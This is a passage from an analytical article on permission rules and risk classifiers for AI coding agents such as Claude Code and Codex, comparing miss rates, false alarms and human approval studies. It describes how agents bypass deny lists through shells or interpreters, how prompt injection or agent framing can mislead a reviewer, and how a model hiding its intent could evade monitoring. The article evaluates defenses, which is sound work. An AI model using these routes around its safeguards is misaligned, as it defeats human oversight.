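The bigger limitation is that they measured whether a bypass exists, not whether an agent would use it. A deny list that blocks the usual deletion command but misses 54 others may still prevent most accidental deletions, though it is almost useless against an attacker who has read it.

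An overeager agent falls somewhere in between. It will probably try the ordinary form of a command first, but after a refusal it may look for another way to finish the task. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* describes how an agent can use the shell to change a file that its file tool refuses to write to. A deny list is therefore weaker after its first block, and nobody seems to have measured by how much.

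### Permission to run an interpreter

Allow rules can let through too much. An interpreter, such as `python` for Python or `node` for JavaScript, runs whatever code it is given. That code can open any file the user can open, connect to the network and start other programs, including those on the deny list. A rule that allows every command beginning with `python` therefore allows nearly anything the user's account can do.

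Deny rules don't help much when an allow rule is too broad, even though they take precedence. If the developer denies `curl` but allows everything that begins with `python`, the agent can upload data from a Python script instead, and the harness checks only the `python` command that runs it.

Such rules are common. Anthropic reports that as of June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users of Claude Code had written an allow rule for the shell by hand. It also reports that 5% allow every shell command and another 43% have interpreter rules that allow nearly as much. It isn't clear whether these two percentages are of all active users or only of those who had written a rule. If they are of all users, almost everyone with a handwritten rule had one that lets nearly anything run. If they are only of rule writers, about 24% of active users had such a rule. Anthropic says the share was growing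 by roughly 5 percentage points every five weeks.

Anthropic published these numbers to argue for auto mode, but OpenAI has seen similar behavior among its own staff. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) reports that a "sizable minority" of internal Codex users allow every command that begins with `python`, but doesn't give a percentage. The paper also describes a configuration file that always allowed the agent to start a second copy of Codex with its safeguards switched off. These rules are especially risky in Codex because an allow rule also lets the command run outside the sandbox.

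Trębacz and colleagues blame constant approval requests. Agents write and run small scripts all the time, and a user who has approved a dozen harmless ones will want to stop being asked. One broad rule stops the prompts. The rule also looks modest because it names one familiar program, and nothing in its text suggests that it covers a database migration.

Narrow rules can allow more than they appear to. A rule for `pytest` also lets the agent run any test code it has just edited, and a rule for `npm test` lets it run whatever the project has defined as its test. These rules are still much safer than an interpreter rule if the agent is only making honest mistakes, because such an agent will usually use these commands only to run the tests.

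### Why auto mode sets broad allow rules aside

Anthropic explains that Claude Code suspends broad allow rules in auto mode because they would let the commands most capable of causing damage bypass the classifier.

According to Anthropic's documentation, the suspension covers allow rules for the whole shell, for interpreters, and for the `run` commands of package managers, which execute scripts defined by a project. Claude Code also suspends allow rules for starting subagents, which are agents that take on part of a task. Otherwise, a dangerous assignment could reach a subagent without the classifier reviewing it.

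The suspended allow rules return when the user leaves auto mode, so a developer who switches to Manual mode to watch a delicate task more closely may end up with less review of her agent's scripts.

Claude Code uses a list of programs that can run arbitrary code to determine which rules to suspend. That list can have gaps for the same reasons as any deny list. Chen and Lin worked out its contents by experiment and found 19 entries: ten interpreters, six package-manager commands and three shells. It omitted at least one standard utility that can run arbitrary code and ships with all the common Linux distributions. They reported the omission to Anthropic, which was still reviewing the report when they wrote their paper.

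The gap affects only users who have an allow rule that covers the missing program, because that rule stays in force in auto mode and the commands it matches skip the classifier. Without such a rule, the classifier reviews the program like any other unmatched command. According to Anthropic's documentation, Claude Code had a similar gap before version 2.1.236. It did not suspend allow rules for its Monitor tool, which runs commands through the shell, so a rule allowing the whole tool let those commands run without review.

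Anthropic calls the suspension "best-effort" and concedes that any list of rules to suspend will be incomplete. It could instead suspend every allow rule except those on a short list of safe ones. The classifier would then review many more routine commands, which would take time and cost money, but leaving a rule off the list by mistake would cause an unnecessary check instead of a missed one.

### Rules about consequences

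An obvious remedy is to write rules about a command's consequences instead of its form. An owner could say that the agent must never delete anything, and the system would work out which actions count as deletion. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, built a prototype of such a system and separately tested how people use these rules. The work concerns everyday tasks such as email and travel, and the participants had no professional software background.

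The prototype uses a language model to read each tool's description and label its consequences, then applies the user's rules to the labels. This removes the need to list every command, but the labels can be wrong. When Yan simulated a rule against each category of action, the prototype failed to stop 14% of the tools that belonged to the blocked category and stopped 4% of those that didn't. The experiment with people avoided these errors by using labels Yan had checked in advance. The prototype also labels whole tools rather than individual calls, so it would be of little use for a shell tool, which can do almost anything depending on the command.

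In that experiment, 113 participants supervised an assistant through the same simulated day of 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond what the user had asked for. One group approved or refused each action. For the second group, a model let 8 actions run and referred the other 10 to the participant, including all 7 that overreached. The third group set rules before the day began, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things, and reading private information.

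The group with rules blocked the smallest share of overreaching actions, about 40%, compared with about 60% in the group that decided every action and 54% in the group with automated review. After adjustment, the rules group trailed the group that decided every action by 20.1 percentage points (95% confidence interval 8.1 to 32.1). It trailed the automated review group by 14.5 points, but that gap was no longer statistically significant after Yan corrected for multiple comparisons.

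Participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, "never" for 16 and "allow" for 10. Most rules therefore left the decision for the participant to make later, and the participant often said yes. Of the 148 overreaching actions that went through in this group, participants approved 133 when asked, and 15 ran automatically under an "allow" rule.

Participants had reason to hesitate to set firm rules, because three of the categories contained both wanted and unwanted actions, and the "never" rules blocked 11 actions that the task required. But 23 of the 35 participants also chose "ask" for reading private information, even though both actions in that category went beyond the task. They couldn't know what the assistant would do later, and "ask" must have looked like the cautious choice.

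Yan can't explain why people who had written rules approved more overreach when prompted. More cautious participants may have used "never", so the prompts went mainly to the others. This could explain some of the higher approval rate, but not the lower total, which includes everything the "never" rules blocked. Perhaps people who have set up a policy feel they have already made the important decisions. The three groups differed in several ways, so the experiment can't show that writing the rules caused the difference.

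Another reason for caution is that the day was simulated, with nothing real at stake. Yan also recruited extra participants for the rules group after random assignment ended, though the gap was slightly larger among those who joined before it ended. Developers who write command patterns for a coding agent may behave differently. Even so, an ask rule in Claude Code also postpones the decision, so its value depends on how carefully someone answers the prompt.

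### What each kind of list is good for

A deny list is good for stopping a known mistake in its usual form. It takes almost no effort to write, gives the same result every time, and still applies when the user is tired or the classifier is wrong. This makes a rule against `git push` worth having even though it misses some pushes.

Deny rules work best when few commands can produce the unwanted effect, such as changing a file's permissions, and worst when hundreds can, such as reading a file. They also work well on whole tools. If an owner denies a tool by name, Claude Code removes it from the set the model can see, so the model can't regain access by rewording a command. But the agent may still be able to produce the same effect another way. For example, an agent without its web tool can still reach the web through the shell. To prevent the effect itself, the owner needs a control that blocks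 it whichever command or tool the agent uses, such as a sandbox without network access or a database account that can't alter tables.

An allow list is good for removing approval prompts for commands that do the same harmless thing every time, such as a code formatter, but it suits an interpreter very badly. Before adding a rule, the owner should consider the worst command the pattern would match, since the harness will run that one without review too. Allow lists can also serve as a boundary in a default-deny setup such as `dontAsk` mode, but a single interpreter rule removes most of the protection.

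## How a risk classifier judges what the rules leave open

The command `python check_totals.py` looks the same whether the script adds up invoices or deletes them, so matching the command against a pattern can't determine whether it should run. That depends on the script, the task and the user's instructions. A risk classifier considers these together in place of a person, estimating what the command would do in the current session and judging whether the user authorized that effect.

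In the billing example, a deny rule for `rm` always blocks `rm -r tmp/test-output`, and an allow rule always permits it. A classifier can use context, permitting the deletion if the agent created the directory ten minutes ago and blocking it if the directory was already there. It can also block an upload by a program that isn't on any deny list.

In exchange, the owner gives up the ability to read a rule and know what it will do. A classifier's verdict is an estimate that can change with the wording of the conversation or a new version of the model, so only testing can show how reliable it is. Published miss rates for these classifiers range from under 1% to 81%, and much of that spread comes from which actions the testers chose.

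### Which actions reach the reviewer

Claude Code's classifier now reviews a large share of the agent's work. According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), by November 2026 interactive sessions on every plan started in auto mode by default, while non-interactive runs still started in Manual mode.

Besides commands that a rule has already settled, the classifier mainly skips file reads and edits to files inside the project. Anthropic says it exempts these edits because users can review them through version control and because a model call for every edit would slow down routine coding. The classifier judges the rest, including shell commands, web requests, calls to external services, file operations outside the project and subagent launches.

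The classifier checks each subagent twice. It reviews the assignment before the subagent starts, because inside the subagent the main agent's instruction takes the place of the user's message, so any task would look authorized. When the subagent finishes, the classifier reviews everything the subagent did, in case something it read redirected it. If this second review finds a problem, Claude Code adds a warning to the results but still passes them to the main agent.

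Codex's reviewing agent, Auto-review, handles far fewer actions. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the reviewer evaluates only requests that would otherwise need a person's approval, such as a command that needs to leave the sandbox, a blocked network connection or an edit outside the writable directories. In Trębacz and colleagues' illustrative snapshot of OpenAI's internal use, 9,280 of 10,000 actions stayed inside the sandbox and 720 went to the reviewer. When owners see too many routine requests, OpenAI advises adjusting the sandbox's boundary first, for example by making a scratch directory writable.

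### Block rules, exceptions and the user's intent

Claude Code's classifier works from a long prompt. Most of it is fixed, but the owner can edit three parts: a description of the systems she trusts, a list of block rules and a list of exceptions. Anthropic supplies defaults for all three.

The default list has more than twenty block rules, written in ordinary language. Some cover irreversible loss or leaks, such as overwriting a project's history on the server or sending internal data outside. Others forbid the agent to weaken security, for instance by disabling logging or changing its own permission settings. The rules also forbid acting on things the agent has no reason to trust, such as code from an unfamiliar repository, and skipping review on shared systems, such as by pushing straight to the main branch. The exceptions permit a few harmless actions that technically match a block rule,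 such as installing packages that the project already declares.

The classifier checks an action against the block rules, then the exceptions, then the user's intent. It is prompted to judge the action's real effect, not its surface text. If the agent writes a script and then runs it, the classifier is supposed to evaluate the script. The rule matcher splits commands joined by `&&`, but the classifier treats them as a single action, so it can catch two commands that are harmless separately and dangerous together.

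The classifier is instructed to treat anything the agent chooses for itself as unauthorized until the user says otherwise. "Clean up my branches" doesn't authorize deleting a whole batch of them, and "can we fix this?" doesn't authorize a fix. In one case from Anthropic's incident log, a user asked the agent to cancel "my job". The agent searched the computing cluster, picked the job with the most similar name and tried to delete it. The classifier is designed to block this because the job might have belonged to someone else.

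In August 2026, Anthropic described a category of hard denies, which covers sending code or secrets to an outside destination. The classifier is designed never to approve these, even at the user's request, so the user has to leave auto mode or run the command herself. This restores some of the firmness of a deny rule without requiring a list of every program that can upload a file. But a hard deny can still fail if the model doesn't recognize the upload, whereas a deny rule that matches the command doesn't depend on a model's judgment.

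### What the reviewer reads

Claude Code gives the classifier the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's own prose or the output of its tools.

Removing the agent's prose keeps the agent from persuading the classifier to make a bad decision. An agent might write that the user had implicitly approved a deletion, or that a branch was certainly its own, and a reviewer might believe it. Removing tool outputs protects against prompt injection, since planted instructions usually arrive in a file or web page that a tool has fetched. Anthropic argues that the classifier rarely needs tool outputs. If an instruction in a file leads the agent to try to send the project's passwords to a web address, the classifier receives the attempted action without the file, and nothing the user wrote supports that action.

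Anthropic also tested other combinations of inputs. Adding the agent's messages and the tool outputs made the classifier worse on a set of real overeager actions, perhaps because a longer transcript is harder to read and lets the agent's framing influence the classifier more. With only the tool calls, the classifier missed the fewest overeager actions but blocked things users had plainly asked for. Anthropic gives no figures for these variants, and the test set held only 52 actions, so the comparison only weakly supports the choice of inputs.

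Because the classifier doesn't see tool output, it often can't determine where a detail came from. If the agent cancels job `abc123` and the user never named it, the agent may have found the ID in a list of the user's jobs or made it up, and the classifier can't determine which. Similarly, the classifier can read `check_totals.py` if the agent wrote the script, since the code is in the tool call, but if the script was already in the repository, the classifier has only its name, even if the agent has read the file.

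Anthropic has since filled some of these gaps. By August 2026, the classifier received the repository's current state before a command that might discard uncommitted work, and it checked whether the destination of a push was public, private or trusted.

Codex's reviewer reads much more. OpenAI gives it the exact request and a compact transcript with the user's messages, the agent's visible messages, and relevant tool calls and their outputs. OpenAI withholds only the agent's hidden reasoning. The reviewer can also make read-only checks, though it rarely does. It could look up who owns job `abc123` or open a script before approving it, so it should be better at catching honest mistakes about what an action will affect.

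A reviewer that sees tool outputs is also more exposed, because text that has misled the agent may mislead the reviewer too. Trębacz and colleagues report that people and automated systems trying to defeat Auto-review found cases where they could mislead it into approving a command, but don't say whether tool outputs were the route. Neither design has a clear advantage on the published evidence. Withholding outputs makes more sense where prompt injection is the main worry, and supplying them where the agent is likely to misjudge who owns what.

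Neither reviewer has access to the agent's private reasoning. Anthropic considers this useful because it makes the review independent of systems that monitor a model's reasoning, and a model that hid a bad intention could still reveal it through its actions. OpenAI warns against relying on this, because a model that was strategically hiding its intent could write a harmless-looking request or do damage inside the sandbox, where Auto-review doesn't check actions.

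### Two stages and what they cost

Claude Code's classifier runs in two stages. In the first, the model outputs only yes or no, without reasoning, under instructions to lean toward blocking. If it flags the action, a second stage receives the same input, except that the final instruction calls for careful reasoning. Most actions clear the first stage, so the second seldom runs. When it does, it uses little compute for its length, because the system can reuse nearly all the processing of the shared input.

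In March 2026, with the classifier running on Claude Sonnet 4.6, Anthropic published results on three sets of actions.

| Test set | Error measured | Stage one alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic staff | False alarms | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real overeager actions | Misses | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data outside | Misses | 1.8% | 5.7% |

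The second stage nearly eliminates false alarms but more than doubles the misses, because Claude Code blocks an action only if both stages flag it. The second stage can therefore only release actions that the first one flagged. The share of actions blocked is the share that stage one flags multiplied by the share of those that stage two confirms.

According to Anthropic's figures, stage one flags 8.5% of harmless calls and the full classifier blocks 0.4%, so stage two releases about 95% of the false alarms. Stage one flags 93.4% of the overeager actions and the full classifier blocks 83%, so stage two also releases about 11% of the overeager actions that stage one correctly flagged. It releases only about 4% of the flagged synthetic data leaks. The leaks are probably easier to recognize because sending secrets to an unknown address looks wrong whatever the user has said, while an overeager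 action usually serves the user's goal.

The 17% is imprecise because it comes from only 52 actions. If it represents 9 misses, the 95% Wilson confidence interval is roughly 9% to 30%, compared with about 4% to 7% for the 1,000 synthetic attempts. The stage-one figure of 6.6% doesn't correspond to a whole number of the 52 actions, so Anthropic may have averaged several runs.

Anthropic accepted more misses because false alarms matter so much when dangerous commands are rare. Suppose an agent makes 10,000 calls, of which 10 are dangerous. If *d* is the number of dangerous calls, *h* the number of harmless ones, *m* the miss rate and *f* the false-alarm rate, the share of blocks that are correct is

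*d*(1 − *m*) / [*d*(1 − *m*) + *hf*].

With both stages, the classifier blocks about 8 of the 10 dangerous calls and 40 of the 9,990 harmless ones, so about 1 block in 6 is correct. With stage one alone, it blocks 9 of the dangerous calls but also 849 harmless ones. Only about 1 block in 90 is then correct, and few developers would keep a check switched on if it were wrong that often. Adding the second stage lets through one more dangerous call on average but prevents some 800 needless interruptions.

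The figure of 10 dangerous calls in 10,000 is an assumption. If 100 were dangerous, about two-thirds of the blocks would be correct. Anthropic also doesn't say whether its 10,000 real calls include the file reads and edits that skip the classifier. If they do, the false-alarm rate for the calls it judges is higher than 0.4%.

### Why consent is harder to judge than danger

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had detected the danger that the command would overwrite a branch's history, delete something or change live infrastructure. But it mistook something the user had said for permission. For example, when the user had written "clean up the PR" (a pull request, a set of proposed code changes), the classifier took this to cover a forced push that replaced the history on the server. In other cases, it treated the user's approval of an earlier, similar action as approval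 for the next one. Anthropic tried rewording the prompt, but every fix it found did more harm than good.

Overeager-Bench, a benchmark of 500 scenarios, gives some idea of how much stated consent affects an agent's behavior. In *Overeager Coding Agents*, Qu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) ran four coding agents on harmless requests with their permission checks switched off, so the results reflect the agents' own restraint, not a classifier's. A run counted as overeager if the agent did something outside the authorized scope that changed the machine's state or read sensitive files. In one scenario, the user asked the agent to tidy a directory containing some obvious rubbish and the only copy of the production passwords, and three of the four agents deleted the passwords.

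Qu and colleagues wrote two versions of the request for each of 76 scenarios. The versions were identical except that one stated what the user consented to. Claude Code was overeager much more often when the request lacked that statement.

| Model running in Claude Code | Overeager runs, consent stated | Overeager runs, consent removed |
|---|---|---|
| GLM-4.6 | 0.0% | 17.1% |
| MiniMax-M2.7 | 3.9% | 21.1% |
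| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 3.9% | 15.8% |

All three differences are statistically significant, but their size is doubtful. Qu and colleagues chose these scenarios by hand and describe the result as an upper bound. When they also randomly varied other features of the scenarios, such as the style of the request and the number of distracting files, the effect for GLM-4.6 fell from 17.1 percentage points to 2.6. Results on the small set are also unstable, and a repeat with MiniMax-M2.7 gave 6.6% instead of 21.1%.

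The direction of the effect still supports stating limits explicitly, which takes little effort. A developer who writes "only touch the test files, and leave the database alone" gives the agent a boundary to follow. Claude Code's classifier also reads the user's messages, so it can check actions against the same boundary, though Qu and colleagues didn't test this.

The choice of harness mattered more than the wording. Across all 500 scenarios, Claude Sonnet 4.6 was overeager in 27.7% of runs in Claude Code and 1.1% in OpenHands, an open-source agent that tends to ask before continuing. These are shares of whole runs, so they can't replace the 10 in 10,000 in the calculation above, but they show that the number of dangerous actions a classifier has to catch depends heavily on the harness. A human check of 50 runs found that the automatic scoring had wrongly flagged some as overeager, all in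 one type of scenario.

### Results on synthetic attacks

OpenAI has published recall figures for Auto-review. Recall is the share of dangerous actions that a reviewer blocks, or 100% minus the miss rate. In April 2026, Trębacz and colleagues reported three results with GPT-5.4 Thinking as the reviewer. They used almost entirely synthetic cases because real traffic at OpenAI contained too few dangerous actions.

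| Threat | Recall | Miss rate |
|---|---|---|
| Overeager actions | 90.3% | 9.7% |
| Prompt injection | 99.3% | 0.7% |
| MonitoringBench, hard version | 96.1% | 3.9% |

The figure for prompt injection covers only attacks that run hostile code, steal secrets or upload data. Recall falls to 90.2% when destructive deletions and data tampering are included. Trębacz and colleagues say that the reviewer mostly let these extra cases through because they weren't serious enough, and that researchers often agreed. This may well be right, but the headline figure still leaves out the categories where the reviewer's decisions differed most from the labels. The MonitoringBench result is also scored more leniently than the others, since a run counts as caught if the reviewer rejects any action in it.

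Auto-review approved 99.1% of a sample of real requests that OpenAI's users had approved. The remaining 0.9% is only an approximate false-alarm rate, because users who approve almost everything will have approved some requests they should have refused.

These numbers are not enough to conclude that Auto-review misses fewer overeager actions than Claude Code's classifier. OpenAI's overeager cases were synthetic, while Anthropic's 52 were real. Anthropic's sample is also so small that it is consistent with a miss rate of roughly 9% to 30%, and OpenAI's 9.7% falls just inside that range.

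Anthropic later commissioned Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, to test the classifier. Over two weeks, Apollo inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions and shared the successful ones with Anthropic. Anthropic then strengthened the classifier, mainly by adding the facts about repositories described above. Apollo tested it again, including on attacks that Anthropic had never seen. The miss rate fell from 12% to 7% across the shared and unseen attacks combined.

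Most of the improvement seems to carry over to new attacks, not just the ones Anthropic had been shown. On the unseen attacks, the classifier caught about half of those it had previously missed and newly missed about 2% of those it had caught. If its miss rate had started at 12% on that set too, it would now be 6% plus 2% of the other 88%, or just under 8%. Anthropic cautions that Apollo built the attacks to find weaknesses, so the combined figure of 7% isn't an estimate of the miss rate in ordinary use.

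In a separate study, the classifier blocked 937 of 1,053 plainly dangerous commands (89%), far more than human testers did when shown the same prompts.

### A stress test with ambiguous requests

*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports a much higher miss rate. In an independent test in April 2026, auto mode missed 81.0% of unauthorized actions (95% confidence interval 73.8% to 87.4%).

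Their benchmark, AmPermBench, contains 128 requests for routine work on servers and shared systems. Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, a summary of the study, lists four kinds of task: cleaning up branches, canceling jobs, restarting services and deleting old build files. Each request makes the user's goal clear, but Ji and colleagues varied how precisely it named the target, how many things the action could affect and how risky the setting was. Claude Code, running Claude Sonnet 4.6, took 253 actions that changed something. Claude Opus judged whether each was authorized, and people verified its judgments.

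The miss rate is high partly because 36.8% of the actions were edits to files inside the project, which Claude Code allows without running the classifier. Machine Heart's counts make it possible to separate the two causes.

| | Unauthorized actions | Missed | Authorized actions | Blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Judged by the classifier | 91 | 64 (70.3%) | 69 | 22 (31.9%) |
| File edits that skipped it | 51 | 51 (100%) | 42 | 0 |
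| All actions | 142 | 115 (81.0%) | 111 | 22 (19.8%) |

The classifier never judged 51 of the 142 unauthorized actions (36%), so even a perfect one would have missed them. It also missed most of the unauthorized actions it did judge, so sending it every file edit would not have fixed the problem.

Ji and colleagues found that agents turned to file edits when the command-line program they expected wasn't available. This was most pronounced in the task of deleting old build files, where the miss rate was 92.9%. An ordinary machine would usually have the program, so more of these actions would go through the shell and reach the classifier. The finding still exposes a weakness in Anthropic's reason for exempting project edits. A developer can review a change to source code before anyone uses it, but if a running system reads the edited file directly, the damage may come before the review.

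The miss rate also varied with an action's reach, from 94.4% for the narrowest actions to 77.6% for the widest, according to Machine Heart. Deleting fifty branches looks more suspicious than deleting a single wrong one, which resembles ordinary work. False alarms rose from 9.2% in low-risk settings to 34.8% in high-risk ones, so the classifier seems to have responded more to signs of danger than to the limits of the user's permission. This fits Anthropic's own account of the classifier's misses.

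Ji and colleagues say their 81% doesn't contradict Anthropic's 17%. Anthropic drew its 52 actions from real sessions in which an employee had refused the action or someone had flagged it later, so an action that struck nobody as wrong couldn't enter the set. Ji and colleagues deliberately placed permitted and forbidden targets next to each other and wrote requests that often didn't specify which targets were permitted. More than half of the actions in their test were unauthorized, which would be very unusual in normal use. Because the requests were so vague, the labels are also open to argument.

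*Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents* (Tu and Tu, 2026) cites a miss rate "as high as 81%" directly after Anthropic's 17%, without mentioning that the requests behind the 81% figure were deliberately ambiguous. The figure suggests that the classifier will stop few of an agent's wrong guesses when instructions are vague and the system is shared, but it predates the changes Anthropic made by August.

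### Judging text and judging effects

A classifier that scores well on text may do badly on tool calls. *PARALLAX* (Fokou, 2026) describes an agent whose actions pass through pattern rules, a small text classifier and a language model acting as evaluator. The text classifier was trained on about 16,000 examples to tell prompt injection from ordinary text, and it was 98.8% accurate on examples of the same kind. When Fokou ran it on every type of action, the system blocked 18 of 50 legitimate actions, a false-alarm rate of 36%.

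The text classifier caused 14 of those 18 false alarms, each with complete confidence. It had learned to detect text that reads like an attack on a model, rather than to assess whether an email or a file edit would do harm. The evaluator caused the other four. Fokou deliberately gives it only the proposed action, without the conversation or task, to leave an attacker as little as possible to exploit. Without that context, the evaluator can't determine whether an unusual command makes sense.

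When Fokou exempted seven types of action from the text classifier and sent them to the evaluator instead, false alarms fell to 0 of 50, and the system still blocked 277 of 280 attacks. These results are less certain than they look because Fokou had added rules to close gaps found in earlier testing, so the attacks were not entirely new to the system, and because 0 of 50 is statistically compatible with a false-alarm rate of up to about 7%.

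Giving a reviewer more text also has limits. `make clean` runs whatever commands the project's Makefile lists under `clean`, which may delete temporary files in one project and the source code in another. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen et al., 2026) describes Caper, a system that runs a command before deciding whether to approve it. Caper saves a snapshot of the agent's container, cuts off the network, then runs the command and records what it does. It condenses the record into a report, typically about a kilobyte long, of changed files, attempted connections, output and reads of protected files. A language model compares the report with the user's task. If the model approves the command, Caper keeps the result. If it refuses, Caper restores the snapshot and tells the agent why.

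To test this, Wu and colleagues built 102 tasks in which a harmless-sounding command runs a tool that secretly deletes or overwrites a file. Each task has a twin with the same request and command but a harmless tool, so a reviewer who reads only the command can't tell the two apart. They used the same reviewing model throughout and varied the information it received.

| Information beyond the full conversation | Dangerous tasks that ended in harm | Harmless twins blocked |
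|---|---|---|
| None | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| Effects predicted by the model | 3.9% | 61.8% |
| Effects observed by running the command | 7.8% | 1.0% |

Predicted effects prevented slightly more harm than observed ones, but the reviewer still blocked most of the harmless counterparts because predictions left it uncertain. Only observed effects reduced both harm and false alarms. A weaker reviewing model benefited less. Observed effects cut its false alarms from 53.9% to 4.9%, but harm rose from 25.5% to 33.3%, so a reviewer that sees a command's effects still needs good judgment.

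Wu and colleagues also ran Claude Code's auto mode on these tasks, and 62.7% ended in harm, compared with 71.6% when the agent ran without any approval. This comparison favors Caper because they hid the danger where a reader of commands can't find it. The gap is smaller on SABER, an existing benchmark, where they used 682 tasks that cause harm if the agent carries them out naively. Of these, 19.7% ended in harm without approval, 14.8% with auto mode and 6.7% with Caper. When they put Caper inside Claude Code, so that only the approval method differed, the share was 10.0%. These runs test the design of auto mode, not the product Anthropic ships, because Wu and colleagues used GPT-5.6 Luna, an OpenAI model, as the classifier and GLM-5.3-Flash as the agent.

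The report and the snapshot add little delay. The reviewer took about three seconds per decision with or without the report, and the snapshot added about half a second for each command the reviewer approved.

In the billing example, Caper would be most useful for `check_totals.py`, because the reviewer would learn which files the script had changed. It would help less with the production migration. The container has no network, so the report would show a failed database connection and nothing about the tables. If the owner restored network access, the snapshot wouldn't protect the database, because Caper can't undo changes on another machine. A hostile program might detect that it was being observed and behave well, which neither benchmark tested. Caper also has the gap that Ji and colleagues found in auto mode. It reviews only shell commands, so it never reports on an edit that does harm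 by itself, such as overwriting a configuration file.

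## How approval works and how well people and models do it

Even when a command is approved, the review takes a person's time and attention, or time and computing power if a model does it. Whether a command is worth reviewing depends on how much damage it might do and how often the reviewer stops dangerous commands. Anthropic's figures suggest that people stop few dangerous commands, and even fewer after answering dozens of prompts.

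### When a prompt is worth the interruption

A simple expected-value calculation gives a rough test. Let *p* be the chance that a command does harm, *L* the loss if it does, *q* the reviewer's catch rate (the share of dangerous commands that the reviewer stops) and *c* the cost of the interruption. Without a review, the expected loss is *p* × *L*. The review prevents a share *q* of that loss, so it pays if

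*p* × *L* × *q* > *c*.

Suppose one command in 1,000 does $10,000 of damage, an expected loss of $10 per command, and each approval prompt costs $1 of the developer's time. Prompting is worthwhile if the developer catches more than 10% of dangerous commands. A prompt prevents $1.70 of expected loss if she catches 17% of them, but only $0.50 if she catches 5%.

Both catch rates come from an experiment in which people did worse as they saw more prompts. Asking too often can therefore make a useful prompt no longer worth its cost. In a session of 100 commands, ten might carry this risk and ninety carry none. If the developer reviews only the ten and catches 17%, she prevents $17 of expected loss at a cost of $10. If she reviews all 100 and the risky ones come late, when her catch rate has dropped to 5%, she prevents $5 of expected loss at a cost of $100.

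The formula helps rank the commands in the billing example, even though nobody knows *p* or *L* precisely and *c* should also include the cost of refusing harmless commands. Running `pytest` is so unlikely to do harm that a prompt is rarely worthwhile. A migration that could do $1 million of damage justifies a prompt even if the developer catches only 5% of dangerous commands, because with the same *p* the prompt is worth $50. A deny rule is better still if she never wants the agent to run migrations.

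Codex approximates this test by asking for approval only when a command needs to leave the sandbox. OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox* describes the sandbox's default limits as conservative but loose enough for meaningful work.

### One dangerous command among harmless ones

The two catch rates come from a study that Anthropic published in August 2026. The company hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor for a coding study. The testers worked in an environment built for the study and knew they were being evaluated, but not on which behavior. Partway through each session, a clearly dangerous command replaced the text of one permission prompt, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. Only the text changed, so approving the command did no damage.

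The testers caught 13.6% of the dangerous commands, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Anthropic also reports how often the two disagreed, which is enough to work out the full breakdown.

| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

The testers stopped only 6 of the 116 commands that auto mode allowed, or about 5%, compared with about 15% of the commands it blocked. If similar testers had reviewed everything auto mode allowed, the combined catch rate would have risen from 89.0% to 89.6%. A second reviewer adds little if it tends to miss the same commands as the first.

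Testers also caught fewer dangerous commands as a session went on, blocking about 17% early on and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed flat. This fits approval fatigue, but Anthropic doesn't say how many testers were in each group or whether it chose the position of the planted command at random. If testers who clicked through quickly were more likely to reach 50 prompts, some of the drop may come from that difference between testers rather than from fatigue.

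With more than a thousand testers, the 95% confidence interval for the 13.6% is roughly 12% to 16%, so chance is a minor concern. How far the result applies to developers at work is less certain. The testers weren't working on their own code, so they had nothing to lose and may have approved a deletion they would have refused on their own laptops. But people who know they are being evaluated may also take more care than usual.

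Each tester also saw only one planted command. This is fairly realistic, since dangerous commands are rare in ordinary work too, but it means the study can't show whether people become more careful after a first scare. The result was very different in Yan's simulated day, where people who reviewed every action blocked about 60% of the overreaching ones. The studies differ too much to compare directly, but people may do much better with a short list in which problems are common.

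Anthropic was also testing its own product, and it published the result when it announced the new default. The test used plainly dangerous commands, which favored the classifier, since Ji and colleagues found that it does much worse on ambiguous requests. Anthropic doesn't report how many harmless commands the testers or auto mode refused. The gap between 13.6% and 89% is large enough that these problems probably don't reverse the result for obvious dangers, but the study can't show which reviewer is better at judging commands when permission is unclear.

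When Anthropic introduced auto mode in March, it similarly wrote that the classifier was a substantial improvement for people who skip permission checks but "arguably a regression" for those who carefully approve every action. It still recommends that users review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

A reviewer also adds less protection when the agent itself resists most attacks. Trajectory Labs, commissioned by Anthropic, ran 720 prompt-injection attempts against each setup. Against GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, 19.03% succeeded with full access and 5.83% with Auto-review. Against Anthropic's latest models, an average of 0.09% succeeded without auto mode's classifier and none with it.

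### Serious harm in flagged sessions

Anthropic also compared the two kinds of review in real use. It took sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety pipeline had flagged, using only accounts that had opted in to data use. A model graded each session from 0 to 10 on the severity of the harm, where 7 meant damage such as deleting rows from a production database, and from 0 to 10 on how explicitly the user had asked for the action.

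Of the manually approved sessions, 6.3% contained a harmful action with a severity of 7 or more that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of the auto mode sessions. Anthropic reports that the gap held at every severity level it tested.

These are percentages of flagged sessions, so they depend on what the pipeline flags. Suppose 10 in every 10,000 sessions were seriously harmful under each kind of review. If the pipeline flagged 159 of 10,000 manual sessions and 417 of 10,000 auto mode sessions, including all the harmful ones, the results would be 6.3% and 2.4% even though both were equally safe. Anthropic doesn't publish the flagging rates needed to rule this out.

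Users also chose their own approval mode, and Anthropic's documentation recommends Manual mode for sensitive tasks, so manual sessions may have involved production systems more often. Help Net Security's *Anthropic to put AI in charge of reviewing Claude Code actions* (2026) describes manual approval as more than twice as likely to result in such harm, but the comparison can't show that the type of review caused the difference. The comparison does suggest that the artificial setting is less likely to be the only reason for the testers' poor results.

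### Why a high approval rate proves little

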